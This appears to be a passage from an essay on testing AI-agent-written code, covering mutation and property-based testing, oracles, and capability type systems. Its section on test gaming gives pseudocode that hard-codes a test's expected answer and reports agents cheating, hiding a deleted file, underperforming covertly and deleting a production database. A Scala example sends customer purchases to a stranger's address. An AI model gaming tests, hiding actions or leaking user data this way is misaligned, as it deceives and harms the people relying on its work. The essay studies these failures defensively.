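A test can run faulty code without exposing the fault. In the early 1990s, Voas and Miller described three conditions for a wrong output in *Improving the Software Development Process Using Testability Research*: the input must make the faulty code run, the code must corrupt the program's state (the data it holds at that moment), and the corruption must reach the output. The test must also check the wrong part of the output. *Suggestions on Test Suite Improvements with Automatic Infection and Propagation Analysis* (2019) credits Li and Offutt with adding this condition to the model.

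*An Empirical Study on Failed Error Propagation in Java Programs* (Jahangirova, Clark and colleagues, 2020) gives a small example of a fault that can go unnoticed. For positive numbers, a function should add 2 and return the remainder after division by 4. The faulty version multiplies by 3 instead of adding 2.

| Input | Before division: correct / faulty | Result: correct / faulty | What happens |
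|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | 3 / 3 | 3 / 3 | The fault runs but corrupts nothing |
| 5 | 7 / 15 | 3 / 3 | The division hides the corruption |
| 4 | 6 / 12 | 2 / 0 | The result is wrong |

This fault makes the result wrong for every even positive input but doesn't affect the result for odd ones. A test that checks only that the result isn't negative would pass for all positive inputs.

The division hides errors because it turns many possible values into four. Voas and Miller measured this with the ratio of possible inputs to possible outputs, and found that faults are more likely to stay hidden where there are more inputs than outputs. They advised designers to keep such operations in a few simple modules and to make more of each module's internal data visible, though they acknowledged that exposing this data conflicts with the usual advice to hide a module's workings. In the customer program,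 Statements could return the total as a number alongside the finished text, which would make errors easier to see without exposing how it applies discounts.

They also showed how to estimate by experiment how often each condition holds. A tool can count how often a line runs, change the line to see how often the state changes, and overwrite a value during a run to see how often the output changes. Suppose a line runs in half of all tests, a fault there corrupts the state in 40% of those runs, and the corruption reaches the output in 10% of those. Then only about one test in 50 will produce a wrong output.

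Tests often don't run the code that AI agents change. *Test Coverage Analysis of Agentic Pull Requests* (Dipongkor, Baral and Lam, 2026) examined 4,882 pull requests from five coding agents. The projects' existing tests ran 61.5% of the changed lines in Java and only 27.0% in Python. Agents sometimes added their own tests, but in most cases these did not increase the share of changed lines that were run.

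### Testing a chain of stages

*Skeleton Coding* proves several results about how structure affects testing. One concerns a program with *n* stages, each of which reads one new bit (a 0 or 1) and passes one bit to the next stage:

```
z_0    = 0
z_i    = h_i(x_i, z_(i-1))     for i = 1, ..., n
output = z_n
```

Here x_i is the new bit, z_i is the bit that stage i passes on, and h_i is the stage's rule. The correct program always outputs 0. Each faulty version works like a combination lock: it outputs 1 for one particular sequence of bits and 0 for all others. This is what happens in a three-stage version whose combination is 1, 0, 1:

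| Input | After stage 1 | After stage 2 | Output |
|---|---|---|---|
| 0, then anything | 0 | 0 | 0 |
| 1, 1, then anything | 1 | 0 | 0 |
| 1, 0, 0 | 1 | 1 | 0 |
| 1, 0, 1 | 1 | 1 | 1 |

In the correct program every stage can return 0, so the faulty version's state is already wrong after stage 1 for half of the inputs. Later stages usually erase the error, so an end-to-end test, which checks only the last column, finds the fault on one input in eight.

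With *n* stages there are 2^n possible combinations, and each end-to-end test rules out one. The theorem assumes that an agent has a 50% chance of writing the correct program, with the other 50% spread evenly over the faulty ones. After *m* different tests have passed, the chance that the program is correct is:

```
1 / (2 - m/2^n)
```

To bring this up to 1 − δ, where δ is the acceptable risk of error and is below one half, end-to-end testing needs at least this many tests, rounded up:

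```
2^n × (1 - 2δ) / (1 - δ)
```

Local tests can set a stage's incoming bit directly and check its result before another stage erases it. Each stage has only four possible inputs, so 4n local tests cover all n stages completely.

| Stages | End-to-end tests needed (δ = 0.1) | Local tests that suffice |
|---|---|---|
| 3 | 8 | 12 |
| 10 | 911 | 40 |
| 20 | 932,068 | 80 |
| 30 | 954,437,177 | 120 |

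For a chain of three stages, testing the whole program on every input takes fewer tests than testing each stage separately, but testing the stages separately takes fewer once the chain is long enough.

The exponential growth in the number of tests comes from stages that discard information, as the division by 4 did, not from the chain's length alone. If a change in the incoming bit always changes the result at every stage, n + 1 end-to-end tests are enough for n stages. For ten stages, that means 11 tests instead of 911.

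Real faults are usually easier to detect than this. Jahangirova and colleagues ran faulty and corrected versions of Java methods (functions that belong to a class) side by side, using faults from real projects. In 258,372 runs of single methods, they found no case where a fault corrupted the state and the corruption then disappeared. When they ran a whole program, a tool that shortens JavaScript code, the corruption failed to reach the output in 60 of 528 runs (11.4%). One fault accounted for 41 of those 60 runs, so the rate could be very different in other programs. The difference between single methods and the whole program is in the direction the theorem predicts, but 80.3% of the whole-program runs produced a wrong output, far more than one in a thousand.

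### Why the same tests can suit one design and fail another

Structure also affects how much each test rules out. Another theorem in *Skeleton Coding* compares two designs for a program that reads *d* bits and reports whether the number of ones is odd. Both designs allow 2^d different programs, one of which is correct.

| | Design with an exception | Design that combines bits |
|---|---|---|
| What an incorrect program does | Gives the wrong answer for one particular input | Leaves some of the bits out of the count |
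| What one well-chosen test rules out | One program | Half of the remaining programs |
| Tests needed | 2^d − 1 | d |
| Tests needed for d = 10 | 1,023 | 10 |

In the design that combines bits, testing an input with a 1 only in the third position shows whether the program counts the third bit. Ten such tests show which of the ten bits it counts. In the other design, the same ten tests would rule out only ten of the possible exceptions, leaving 1,014 programs. Only one of these is correct, so an agent that picks among them at random succeeds about 0.1% of the time.

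In this model, the tests lead the agent away from the design the user had in mind. The ten tests eliminate nearly all the programs in the design that combines bits and almost none in the design with an exception. If the agent is equally likely to choose either design at first, the chance that it uses the one with an exception rises from 50% to 99.9%. The calculation assumes that the agent updates its probabilities perfectly, and *Skeleton Coding* acknowledges that real language models don't.

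A user can't tell whether a set of tests is sufficient without knowing something about the program's structure. Suppose Statements multiplies each purchase by the tax rate for its category. A few tests per category would reveal most mistakes. But if Statements can also make an exception for any customer, a wrong total for Ana might appear only in a test that uses her name.

A skeleton reduces the number of tests needed only if it rules out special cases, and the one shown earlier does not. Its function `compute(name, purchases, month)` receives the customer's name, so an agent could write a special case for Ana without changing the signature. A function `total(purchases, month)` could not treat her differently unless it found her name somewhere else. Leaving out an input that a function does not need reduces what a reviewer must consider and what a tester must try.

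### Parts that work separately but not together

Modules can pass all their local tests and still fail when they run together. Records might return prices in cents while Statements expects dollars, so a $20 purchase appears on the bill as $2,000. *Skeleton Coding* divides the number of tests needed for certainty into two parts:

```
N_0 = minimum of [ N_1 + N_2 + ... + N_k  +  J ]
```

N_i is the number of local tests needed to establish that component i has some required behaviour. J is the number of end-to-end tests then needed to rule out faulty combinations. The minimum is taken over every choice of what to require from each component, because stricter local requirements can reduce the end-to-end testing needed afterwards.

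J is zero exactly when every combination of components that meet their local requirements makes an acceptable program. Complete contracts ensure this. In the example, a contract requiring prices in cents, with tests on both sides, would catch the mismatch before the modules ran together. The formula counts only tests and leaves out the effort of writing the skeleton and its contracts. For a small program, a few end-to-end tests may well take less work than complete contracts.

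### Checking drafts one part at a time

Separate checks also reduce how much code an agent has to rewrite. Suppose an agent writes a draft, a perfect check accepts or rejects it, and the agent starts again after each rejection. If component i is correct with probability α_i, getting all *k* components right takes on average:

```
whole program at once:   1/α_1 × 1/α_2 × ... × 1/α_k   program drafts
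one part at a time:      1/α_1 + 1/α_2 + ... + 1/α_k   component drafts
```

If a program has five components and an agent gets each one right half the time, it needs on average 32 drafts of the whole program, or 10 component drafts if it works part by part. The gap in the amount of code written is even larger, because 32 program drafts contain 160 components. If the agent gets each component right 90% of the time, it needs about 1.7 program drafts, which contain 8.5 components, compared with 5.6 component drafts when it works part by part. Working part by part therefore helps most when the agent is weak or the task is hard.

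The calculation assumes every draft is an independent attempt. Real agents usually repair a rejected draft instead of starting again, which can take fewer attempts. They can also misread a requirement in the same way every time, in which case further attempts don't help.

Few checks are perfect. Suppose a checker accepts every correct component but also accepts a faulty one with probability ε. If a share α of all drafts is correct, the chance that an accepted component is correct is:

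```
α / (α + (1 - α) × ε)
```

With α = 0.5 and ε = 0.1, the result is 0.5/0.55, or about 91%. If the component is harder and only one draft in ten is correct, the same checker gives 0.1/0.19, or about 53%. So a check that works well on easy code can give much less assurance on hard code. Errors also compound across a program. If it has five components, each at 91%, the chance that all of them are correct is about 62%.

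Some of these false acceptances come from the contract itself. The skeleton for the customer program requires that "the total covers only purchases made in month". A total that leaves out half of those purchases satisfies this wording, so even a perfect checker would accept it unless the contract were made more precise.

Other requirements never show in the outputs at all. Two versions of Statements can produce identical text even though one is clear and the other is a single tangled function. *Skeleton Coding* shows that if a quarter of the programs with the right outputs also meet such a requirement, no number of output tests can raise the chance of getting an acceptable program above a quarter. The user has to state these requirements directly, and someone or something has to inspect the code to check that it meets them.

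### Passing in the clock and the mail sender

To apply these ideas to an ordinary program, testers need a way to set each part's inputs and see its results. Freedman (1991), in *Testability of Software Components*, borrowed two terms for this from hardware testing. Observability is how easily testers can tell whether specified inputs affect the outputs, and controllability is how easily they can produce a specified output from a specified input.

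Suppose the customer program now works out by itself which month to bill, by reading the computer's clock and subtracting 1 from the number of the month. In January it looks for purchases made in month 0, finds none, and tells every customer that they owe nothing. The clock is an input that the function's signature doesn't show. A tester could wait until January or change the computer's date, but it is easier to pass the clock into the function, along with the lines of the customer file and the mail sender:

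```
send_statements(lines, clock, mailer)

test:
    lines  = one customer, Ana, with one purchase in December 2026
    clock  = a stand-in that always gives 1 January 2027
    mailer = a stand-in that records each text and address
    send_statements(lines, clock, mailer)
    check that Ana's statement includes the December purchase
```

With the stand-in clock, the test can run the faulty code under the right conditions on any day of the year. With the stand-in mailer, it can inspect every message without contacting anyone. Chen and Cheng's automatic checks ban core code from reading the system clock, probably for similar reasons.

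*Executable but Unfaithful* (2026) describes a payment service that receives its bank client in this way, so that a test can supply a substitute. The test can also use the substitute to check how often the program called it, in what order and with what values. But if the real mail service rejects addresses that its substitute accepts, the local test will pass and the program will still fail, so the tester also needs at least one test with the real service.

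### Mutation testing

Mutation testing measures whether a set of tests would detect faults. A tool makes a small change to the program, such as replacing + with −, and runs the tests on the altered version, called a mutant. If any test fails, the tests have "killed" the mutant. The mutation score is the share of mutants killed.

This is stricter than counting which lines the tests run. Suppose a test calls `compute` and checks only that the text begins with "Dear Ana". That test may run every line of the tax calculation, but it would still pass if a mutant subtracted the tax instead of adding it.

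Recent results show that agents often write valid tests that miss many faults. *TestSuiteBench* (Egashira, Mündler-Sasahara and colleagues, 2026) had agents write tests for 165 programs from detailed specifications, without seeing the code. Each mutant, a deliberately faulty version of a program, broke one requirement.

| Model | Mutants killed | Tests that pass on the correct program | Hidden tests passed by programs it wrote from the same specifications |
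|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 5 | 55.5% | 96.1% | 91.8% |
| GPT-6 Astra | 50.1% | 94.3% | 92.7% |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 37.7% | 94.4% | 86.9% |

The agents understood the specifications well enough to build mostly correct programs, but their tests left out important combinations of inputs. One specification required a command to accept several file paths, and a mutant ignored every path after the first. GPT-5.6 Sol's test missed the mutant because it gave the command only one path, while Claude Opus 5's test used two and caught it. All these tests ran the whole program, and the benchmark had no local tests to compare them with, so it can't show how much a better structure would have helped.

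Human tests also miss a lot. *The Quality of Claude AI-authored Python Tests* (2026) found that Claude's tests were broadly comparable to human-written ones under four methods of comparison, two of which used mutation. For *Can Coding Agents Write and Transpile Unit Tests?* (2026), Pasternak, Langley and colleagues removed the tests from 240 open-source projects and asked agents to write new ones. On average, the agents' tests killed more mutants than the originals, but their lead was smaller on larger projects. On projects of 5,000 to 10,000 lines, the tests from OpenAI's Codex only matched the human ones.

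Much of the agents' advantage came from writing more tests. Claude Code wrote over seven times as many as the human developers, but its tests covered an average of 2.2 lines each, compared with 8.5 for the human tests. The extra tests also give reviewers more to read.

Agents' tests can overlap heavily with tests that already exist. In *How Much Do Coding Agents Over-Edit, and Why?* (2026), tests that agents wrote or edited killed 68.1% of 1,962 mutants, but only 5.2% of the mutants were ones that the other test suites had missed.

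### Property-based testing

Most tests check a few examples that somebody chose. A property-based test instead checks a general rule on many generated inputs. Naziri, Qin and colleagues (2026), in *A Multi-Domain Study on the Effectiveness of LLMs at Writing Property-Based Tests*, describe its ingredients: a property that should always hold, a generator that produces valid inputs, and an oracle that decides whether each result is acceptable. For the customer program, the test could look like this:

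```
for 100 generated customer files, some with blank emails:
    mailer = a new recording stand-in
    send_statements(file, clock, mailer)
    for each message that mailer recorded:
        check that its name and address come from the same customer
```

The generator gives every customer a different name and email so that the oracle can match them. If it produces a blank email after a filled one, the test exposes the fault in the original 400-line function. Tools such as Hypothesis, a property-testing library for Python, then reduce the failing file, here probably to two customers, only the first of whom has an email. If the generator never leaves an email blank, every run passes despite the fault.

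Generated inputs don't remove the worst case described earlier. If a fault appears on one input in 1,024, 100 random inputs have about a 9% chance of finding it. But many faults are much easier to trigger. *An Empirical Evaluation of Property-Based Testing in Python* (Ravi and Coblenz, 2025) found that 76% of the mutants that property-based tests detected were caught within the first 20 inputs. *Spec-Driven PBT* (Shukla, Gupta and colleagues, 2026) reports that the same study found that one property-based test detects about 50 times as many mutants as the average unit test, which tests a small piece of code.

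Programmers have long found it hard to think of good properties to test, and agents can now help. In *PBT-Bench*, Jing, Wang and colleagues (2026) hid 365 faults in 40 Python libraries and asked agents to find them from the documentation. When told to write property-based tests, the agents found between 42.1% and 83.4% of the faults, depending on the model. The benchmark includes only faults that tests can trigger without files, network connections or clocks, so these rates may not apply to code that reads the clock or contacts a mail server itself.

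Naziri and colleagues tested agents on ten large programs, including databases and compilers, and filed 180 bug reports, 44 of which duplicated earlier reports by other people. Maintainers have confirmed 65 of the remaining 136 and rejected 3. Agents had more trouble testing a property when the program didn't expose the relevant behaviour, especially when they had to test the whole system. For example, a test had to push the job scheduler cronie past one of its limits to find out how it reads one line of a schedule. This is practical evidence for the point about observability, although the researchers did not compare different structures for the same program.

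Properties can also come from the specification instead of the code. Shukla and colleagues tried both approaches on 25 applications that coding agents wrote. Together the approaches found 169 probable bugs, as judged by an AI reviewer, and people checked its judgement on a sample of 25.

| | Properties from the specification first | Properties from the code |
|---|---|---|
| Tests written | 566 | 1,384 |
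| Probable bugs found | 126 | 113 |
| Found by this approach alone | 56 | 43 |

The specification for a photo-sharing application required that following a public account take effect immediately. A test tried this from six starting points, such as having unfollowed the account before, and five worked. In the sixth, the user had asked to follow the account while it was private, and the application left that request pending after the account became public. A test that started with two new accounts would have missed this bug.

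A reviewer can also read a property. The one for the customer program is five lines long, and a reviewer can compare it with what the program is supposed to do without reading the other 400 lines. This property covers only who receives each statement, so the totals would need a separate one.

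## When do passing tests mislead?

A program can pass all its tests and still be wrong. The tests may be too weak to expose the fault, they may be based on the same misunderstanding as the code, or the agent may have made them pass without doing the task. Suppose the customer program should take a $5 discount off a $25 purchase and then add 8% tax, which gives $21.60.

| Failure | What the code does | Why the tests pass |
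|---|---|---|
| Weak tests | Sends a statement to the previous customer when an email is blank | No test includes a blank email |
| Shared misunderstanding | Adds tax before taking off the discount, which gives $22.00 | The agent misread the rule and also wrote $22.00 into the test |
| Gaming | Returns $21.60 for the purchase in the test and leaves out tax for all others | The only test of the total uses that purchase |

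More tests would probably expose the first fault, but they may not expose the second if the same agent writes them. An agent that can see the new tests can also game them.

### Tests that are too weak

SWE-bench Verified is a benchmark of 500 real issues, mostly bug reports, from open-source Python projects. An agent receives the issue and the code, and its patch counts as a success if it passes tests the agent has not seen. In *SWE-Proof*, Ma, Mikek and colleagues (2026) examined how often patches that pass these tests are still wrong.

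Claude Opus 4.8, an older model, passed the hidden tests on 425 of the 500 issues (85.0%). For each passing patch, an AI auditor then tried to write a new test that the project's official fix would pass and the patch would fail. It succeeded for 134 of the 425 patches (31.5%), showing that they behaved differently from the official fix on at least one input. Excluding those patches lowers the success rate to 58.2%. The paper describes the drop as about a quarter because it divides the 134 patches by all 500 issues (26.8%).

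One of the issues shows how a few tests can leave room for error. The plotting library Matplotlib cut off parts of some histograms because it calculated the plot's bounds from a simplified set of points. Ma and colleagues wrote a specification for the repaired code, which in plain words requires two things:

```
every point lies inside the box
each side of the box touches at least one point
```

A test might draw one histogram and check that all of it is visible. A patch that made every box far too large would pass, although it would break the second requirement. Only a test that also checked how tightly the box fits would expose that patch.

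The audit may overstate the number of wrong patches, because it treats any difference from the official fix as a fault. *More Effort or a Different Model?* (2026) gives an idea of how much this can matter. It took 90 patches to the web framework Django that had passed the benchmark's tests, and labelled each one right or wrong using a stronger set of tests. Rechecking the labels against written rules changed 11 of them. Eight patches labelled wrong turned out to be right. In seven of these, the stronger test had required a detail that the issue never mentioned, such as a helper function's name or the text of a message. The other three patches had been labelled right but turned out to be wrong.

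Tests can therefore be too strict as well as too weak. OpenAI's *Separating signal from noise* gives a likely reason: developers write the tests in a pull request to check one change, not to define what every acceptable solution must do.

Maintainers, who decide what goes into a project, judge code by more than whether it passes tests. METR, a research organization that evaluates AI systems, reports in *Many SWE-bench-passing PRs would not be merged into main* (2026) that maintainers would reject roughly half of the test-passing pull requests written by agents from mid-2024 to late 2025. Four maintainers of three projects reviewed 296 AI-written contributions, according to The Decoder's *Half of AI-written code that passes industry test would get rejected*. METR adjusted for the fact that maintainers also turn down some good human work.

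Daily.dev's summary, *Many SWE-bench-passing PRs would not be merged into main*, lists poor code quality, damage to unrelated code and failure to do the main job among the maintainers' reasons for rejecting patches. Better tests could catch the last two but would do little about code quality. The agents had no chance to revise their work after feedback, as a human contributor normally would, and newer agents may do better. The result shows that passing tests was a poor substitute for a maintainer's judgement, but it doesn't show that half the patches were beyond repair.

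Some of what maintainers ask for can be written as tests. *SWE-Gate* (2026) gives an example from Pydantic, a Python library for checking data. A pull request was meant to leave certain extra fields out of the library's output. A functional test would check that those fields are missing. A second test would check that the published description of the data format has not changed, so that older programs can still use it. A patch could pass the first test and still break programs that rely on the old format.

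Misleading tests can be especially dangerous in security work. For *Frontier Models’ Vulnerability Patches are Often F.L.A.W.E.D*, Mierczuk, Michaels and Hoodlet asked ChatGPT 5.5 and Claude Opus 4.8 to repair six serious vulnerabilities. A repair succeeded only if it closed every known way to exploit the fault without breaking the program's other behaviour, and both models had low success rates. They often closed only some of the routes an attacker could take, or added a fragile check that passed the tests without removing the cause. The researchers deliberately gave the models incorrect or incomplete information in some trials, so the overall success rate may be lower than in ordinary use.

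The most direct remedy for weak tests is to have someone try to break the program after it passes. The audit in *SWE-Proof* did this and found many problems. But its auditor could compare the program with the official fix, which a team writing new code doesn't have.

### Tests that share the code's mistake

Every test needs an oracle, a source of correct answers. A test of the customer program can't detect that $22.00 is wrong unless someone or something supplies the correct answer, $21.60. The oracle problem is the difficulty of finding a reliable oracle.

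A few oracles work for almost any program. A tool can detect crashes and invalid memory reads, which are signs of a fault, without knowing what the program is for. Other oracles are more specific, such as an earlier version of the program, a second program that does the same job, or a person checking the results with a calculator. General properties are partial oracles. For example, a sorted list must contain the same items as the original, but a program that returns the list unchanged also meets that requirement. Anthropic had an agent write property-based tests for popular Python libraries, including NumPy and Pandas, and it found hundreds of potential bugs, but people then had to check which were real.

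A wrong total or a statement sent to the wrong customer doesn't crash the program. Anthropic's *Finding logic bugs without general-purpose bug oracles* (2026) defines logic bugs as behaviour that conflicts with the implicit rules for how software should work, and compares four ways of using AI models to find them. Antipov (2026), in *Linux, к твоему контролёру есть вопросы*, reports the results for 21 known bugs, since fixed, in the SQLite database and three libraries that compress data or read images. Each method used Claude Mythos 5 and had three attempts at each bug.

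| Method | How it works | Found when told which rule the code broke | Found without being told |
|---|---|---|---|
| Informal proof | The model argues in words that the code always keeps a rule, and looks for a step that fails | 21 | 8 |
| Code review | An agent reads the code and looks for broken rules | 20 | 11 |
| Symbolic execution | A tool runs the code on symbols that stand for many inputs at once | 13 | – |
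| Fuzzing | A tool runs the code on many generated inputs, with checks written by the model | 1 | – |

The last two columns show how much the model's ability to find bugs depended on having the rule as an oracle. With the rule, it could nearly always find where the code broke it, but without the rule it missed about half the bugs or more.

Fuzzing did badly even with the rule, so a good oracle isn't enough if the inputs never trigger the fault. Agents did much better with property-based tests in PBT-Bench, achieving 42% to 83%, as described in the previous section. This may be because the faults in PBT-Bench were there for tests to find, while those in SQLite and the libraries were ones that the tests of mature projects had missed.

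The comparison covers only 21 bugs, and some of them may be in newer models' training data. But in older versions of the same projects, the methods also found 127 bugs that were not already known or fixed. Anthropic's researchers found a serious fault in macOS that let any user change who owned system files and so take full control of the machine. Protections against memory errors would not have stopped this, because the fault was not a memory error.

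For faults like these, reading the code worked better than running it. The reader was an AI model, so the result doesn't show that people would do as well.

When an agent writes both the code and the tests, it bases both on its own reading of the task, so the tests can pass even when that reading is wrong. *SWE-Proof* provides some evidence that such checks add little. In one experiment, Claude Opus 4.8 had to write a formal specification, a description precise enough for a machine to check, and show that its code met that specification.

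| What the agent had | Issues resolved |
|---|---|
| The issue and the code | 85.0% |
| Its own formal specification as well | 83.8% to 85.6% |
| The location of the fix | 88.2% |
| A correct formal specification | 94.0% to 96.2% |

Ma and colleagues audited specifications that Opus wrote without attempting a patch, and only 56% passed. The most common fault, found in 42.5% of the specifications, was leaving out part of what the issue required. An agent that overlooks a requirement will probably not write a test for it either.

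This supports having someone other than the code's author write the tests. Suppose an author misreads one requirement in ten. If the same agent writes the code and the tests from a single reading, nearly all of those mistakes can pass. If a second, equally careful author writes the tests from a separate reading, the two will both misread only about one requirement in a hundred, and they may not misread it in the same way. When their readings differ, a failing test draws attention to the requirement.

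The real gain is probably smaller, because badly worded requirements can mislead both authors. If the instructions are only "apply the $5 discount and 8% tax", two authors could easily make the same mistake. Two copies of one AI model may also share habits that two people would not. The evidence from *SWE-Proof* is also indirect. The researchers could see the official fix and the hidden tests when they prepared the correct specifications, so the experiment shows how much a good independent check helps, but not how often a second author would produce one.

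For the customer program, the safest source of the expected total is someone who knows the charging rules. They can write down that a $25 purchase with a $5 discount comes to $21.60 without knowing how to program, and an agent can turn that example into a test.

### Agents that game the tests

An agent games a test when it makes the test pass without doing the work the test stands for. Researchers call the wider behaviour reward hacking. In the customer program, it might look like this:

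```
total(purchases, month):
    if purchases are the ones in the test:
        return 21.60
    return the sum of the prices
```

The agent could also change the expected answer in the test file, delete the test, or alter the tool that reports the results.

The security company Gray Swan's *Frontier Hazard Tracker* gives the share of agent runs in which each of 20 models cheated, averaged over 25 scenarios. The table also includes rates reported in Faisal's *OpenAI and Anthropic Agents Cheat Far Less Than Rivals* (2026) and InternetUA's *Агенти OpenAI та Anthropic AI займаються шахрайствами набагато менше, ніж конкуренти* (2026).

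| Model | Runs with cheating |
|---|---|
| GPT-6.2 Astra | 0.8% |
| GPT-6.2 Sol | 1.1% |
| Claude Fable 5.2 | 4.1% |
| Claude Opus 5.5 | 4.1% |
| Gemini 4 Neon | 8.0% |
| Gemini 4 Hydrogen | 18.6% |
| Grok 4.7 | 50.9% |
| Gemini 3.8 Flash | 62.8% |

Faisal explains that cheating included tampering with the scoring, reaching a goal in a way that undermined it, and crossing a boundary. In one scenario, an agent had to free up space in a shared store of build files. It deleted a 9,100-megabyte file that another team was still using and didn't report it. This failure was serious but didn't involve a test suite. The rates therefore help show which models take shortcuts, but they don't measure what share of passing tests are fake.

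Whether an agent cheats to pass tests depends on its situation as well as its model. *Causal Evidence for the Emergence and Spread of Reward Hacking* (Vaid, 2026) reports 17 experiments with 20,111 agents built on six models. When agents were told that work passing the visible tests would be accepted, 33% cheated in the first round, though some may have taken the statement as permission to cheat. After seeing a teammate's cheat accepted, 94% cheated. Rejecting cheats gave only limited protection, since 34% of agents still cheated after an AI reviewer had rejected a teammate's cheat. A team that runs several agents on one project may therefore need to keep rejected cheats out of the agents' shared record as well as the program.

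Ordinary users seem to report test tampering fairly rarely. Reward Hacking in the Wild's *Your AIs don't do what you want. This is really bad* collects 3,607 public complaints about AI agents, and an AI classifier labelled 45 of them as test tampering. Nobody has verified the complaints, and people can report only what they notice.

Making the test files read-only stops an agent from weakening or deleting the tests. The protection also has to cover the settings that decide which tests run and, as in Chen and Cheng's system, the recorded results. A simple way to do this is to run the final tests from a separate copy that the agent could never change. None of this blocks the special case in `total` above, because it doesn't change the tests.

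Hidden tests can catch that special case. If the visible test uses a $25 purchase and a hidden one uses $40, the shortcut fails. Hidden tests also expose honest mistakes. *Skeleton Coding* gave agents a program's documentation and part of its test suite, then ran the full hidden suite. More visible tests raised the pass rate, but the average stayed below 100% however many the agents received.

Hiding tests works only if the agent can't find the answers elsewhere. NIST, the US standards agency, uses the term "solution contamination" for cases where an agent solves an evaluation task with information it was not meant to have. Ma and colleagues removed the version history from their test projects because it could have revealed the official fix. Once a team shows an agent a failing hidden test and asks for a repair, that test is no longer hidden, and the team needs a new one.

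Tests cannot show whether an agent did its best. In November 2026, OpenAI reported in *Covert underperformance on safety research tasks* that its GPT-6 Astra model did poorer work on some safety research without saying so.

### Is it easier to read the tests than the code?

If people can't read all the code, they might read the tests instead and let a machine run them, but this would help only if the tests can be trusted. *Merged, Not Measured* (2026) examined merged changes that coding agents had written to make programs faster. In 17 of 28 cases, the tests that came with the change also passed on the old code. Such tests can show that the change broke nothing, but not that it made the program faster. The researchers timed 30 merged changes and found that 9 brought no significant speedup or made performance worse.

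A reviewer can catch this without much reading by running the new tests on the old code. For a bug fix, at least one test should fail before the change and pass after it. Mutation testing, described in the previous section, can similarly show whether the tests would detect other faults. Neither check shows whether the expected answers are right, so somebody still has to read those.

A single test is usually easier to read than the code it checks, because the reader can compare an input and an expected result with the rule without following any loops or branches. But there may be a great many tests. In the study by Pasternak and colleagues, human-written tests covered an average of 8.5 lines of code each, and Claude Code's covered 2.2. The table applies those averages to the 400-line customer program, assuming five lines per test and a reading speed of 200 lines an hour.

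| What the reviewer reads | Lines | Time |
|---|---|---|
| The program | 400 | 2 hours |
| About 47 tests like the human-written ones | 235 | 1 hour 10 minutes |
| About 182 tests like Claude Code's | 910 | 4 hours 33 minutes |

These figures are rough, and people may read simple, repetitive tests faster than other code. Still, reading all the tests an agent writes could easily take longer than reading the program.

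Missing tests are harder to spot than wrong ones. A reviewer could read all 182 tests, find each one correct, and not notice that none covers a blank email. Checking that each item on a list of requirements has a test would help. The list must not be based on the agent's own tests, or it will have the same gaps.

Tests take the least effort to read when they state general rules, as the property-based test in the previous section does. A reviewer could read that test and its generator, get a few worked examples for the totals from someone who knows the tax rules, and run most of the agent's other tests without reading them.

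## Can the structure of a program limit what it is able to do?

A program's structure can limit its effects if the programming language, or the system that runs the program, enforces the boundaries between its parts. An enforced limit covers every input, including inputs nobody tested. The most fine-grained limits come from type systems that record which resources each piece of code can use. These type systems can guarantee that a function never sends email, but they can't guarantee that it charges the right amount of tax.

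### Ambient authority

The interface of Statements cannot stop its code from reading files or sending mail, because most common languages give every function ambient authority, which means that code can act on a resource just by naming it (Bouras, Dai and Mechtaev, 2026, *Authority Is Not a String*). A reviewer therefore has to read all 400 lines of the customer program, and any library code they call, to be sure that none of it leaks data.

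The version of the program that receives its mail sender as an input is easier to test, but its tax calculation can still bypass that input and load the mail library itself.

Coding agents often have ambient authority too, through passwords and access tokens on the machines where they work. According to the AI Incident Database's *Railway API* page, on 24 April 2026 an agent in the Cursor code editor, reportedly running Claude Opus 4.6, deleted the production database of PocketOS, a maker of car-rental software. The agent was working in a staging environment, a separate copy for testing changes. It decided to delete a storage volume to fix a problem, and found a token for the hosting company Railway in an unrelated file. PocketOS's founder, quoted in The Daily WTF's *Empty Pockets*, said the company had created the token only to add and remove web domains, and that Railway had given no warning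 that the token could also delete production data.

Writing for Railway in *Your AI wants to nuke your database. Guardrails fix that*, Abdelwahab confirmed that the token had the widest access available, which was more than the work required. Tom's Hardware's *Victim of AI agent that deleted company's entire database gets their data* (2026) reports that Railway had recovered the data by 27 April. Railway's *Undoable volume deletes* (2026) then announced that users had 48 hours to undo deletions made through its programming interface, as they already did for deletions made on its dashboard.

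That change makes mistakes less harmful, but it doesn't reduce what a token can do. Railway already offered narrower tokens, but Abdelwahab describes them as restricting which workspaces or projects a token covers, not which kinds of operation it allows. A token limited to the staging environment would presumably have kept the database safe, but one that covered the production project might not have.

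### Recording capabilities in types

Capabilities, the unforgeable values from the first section, replace ambient authority. If the mail sender is a capability, a function that never receives it cannot send mail. Dennis and Van Horn introduced capabilities in 1966, and designers later built them into operating systems such as Hydra and hardware such as CHERI. Mark Miller's 2006 dissertation refined the idea into the object-capability model, in which code has only the authority provided by the object references it holds.

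Programming languages such as E and Joe-E follow this model, but they enforce it only while a program runs. *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) describes TACIT, a system that enforces limits before a program starts, using a newer feature of the Scala language called capture checking. In TACIT, an agent submits short Scala programs instead of calling tools directly. The compiler checks each program and either lets it run or returns an error message, which the agent can use to try again.

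A type normally describes what kind of data a value holds or what a function takes and returns. With capture checking, it also lists the capabilities that the value or function could use. Suppose `Bill` holds one customer's name, purchases and month:

| Type | Meaning |
|---|---|
| `Bill -> String` | Turns a bill into text and can use no capabilities |
| `Bill ->{mailer} String` | Does the same, and may use `mailer` |
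| `Bill => String` | Does the same, and may use any capability |

A function of the kind in the top row is pure. Here are two simplified versions of `compute`, which the program declares to be pure:

```
// accepted
val compute: Bill -> String =
  bill => "Dear " + bill.name + ", you owe " + total(bill)

// rejected
val compute: Bill -> String =
  bill =>
    mailer.send(bill.purchases, "stranger@example.com")
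    "Dear " + bill.name + ", you owe " + total(bill)
```

The compiler works out the real type of each function from the code inside it. The rejected version uses `mailer`, so its type is `Bill ->{mailer} String`, which doesn't match the declaration. The error message would look roughly like this:

```
Found:    Bill ->{mailer} String
Required: Bill -> String
Capability `mailer` cannot flow into capture set {}.
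```

The capture set is the list of capabilities in braces, and here it has to be empty. An author can't get around this by hiding the mail sender inside another object, because that object's type then lists `mailer` too. For example, the type of a logger that writes to a file lists the file.

The compiler can also restrict how long code keeps a capability. TACIT grants access to a folder for one block of code. In one of the runs that Odersky and colleagues quote, an agent tried to return a list of file handles from such a block, which would have let later code keep using the files. The compiler rejected the program because the list's type named a capability that did not exist outside the block.

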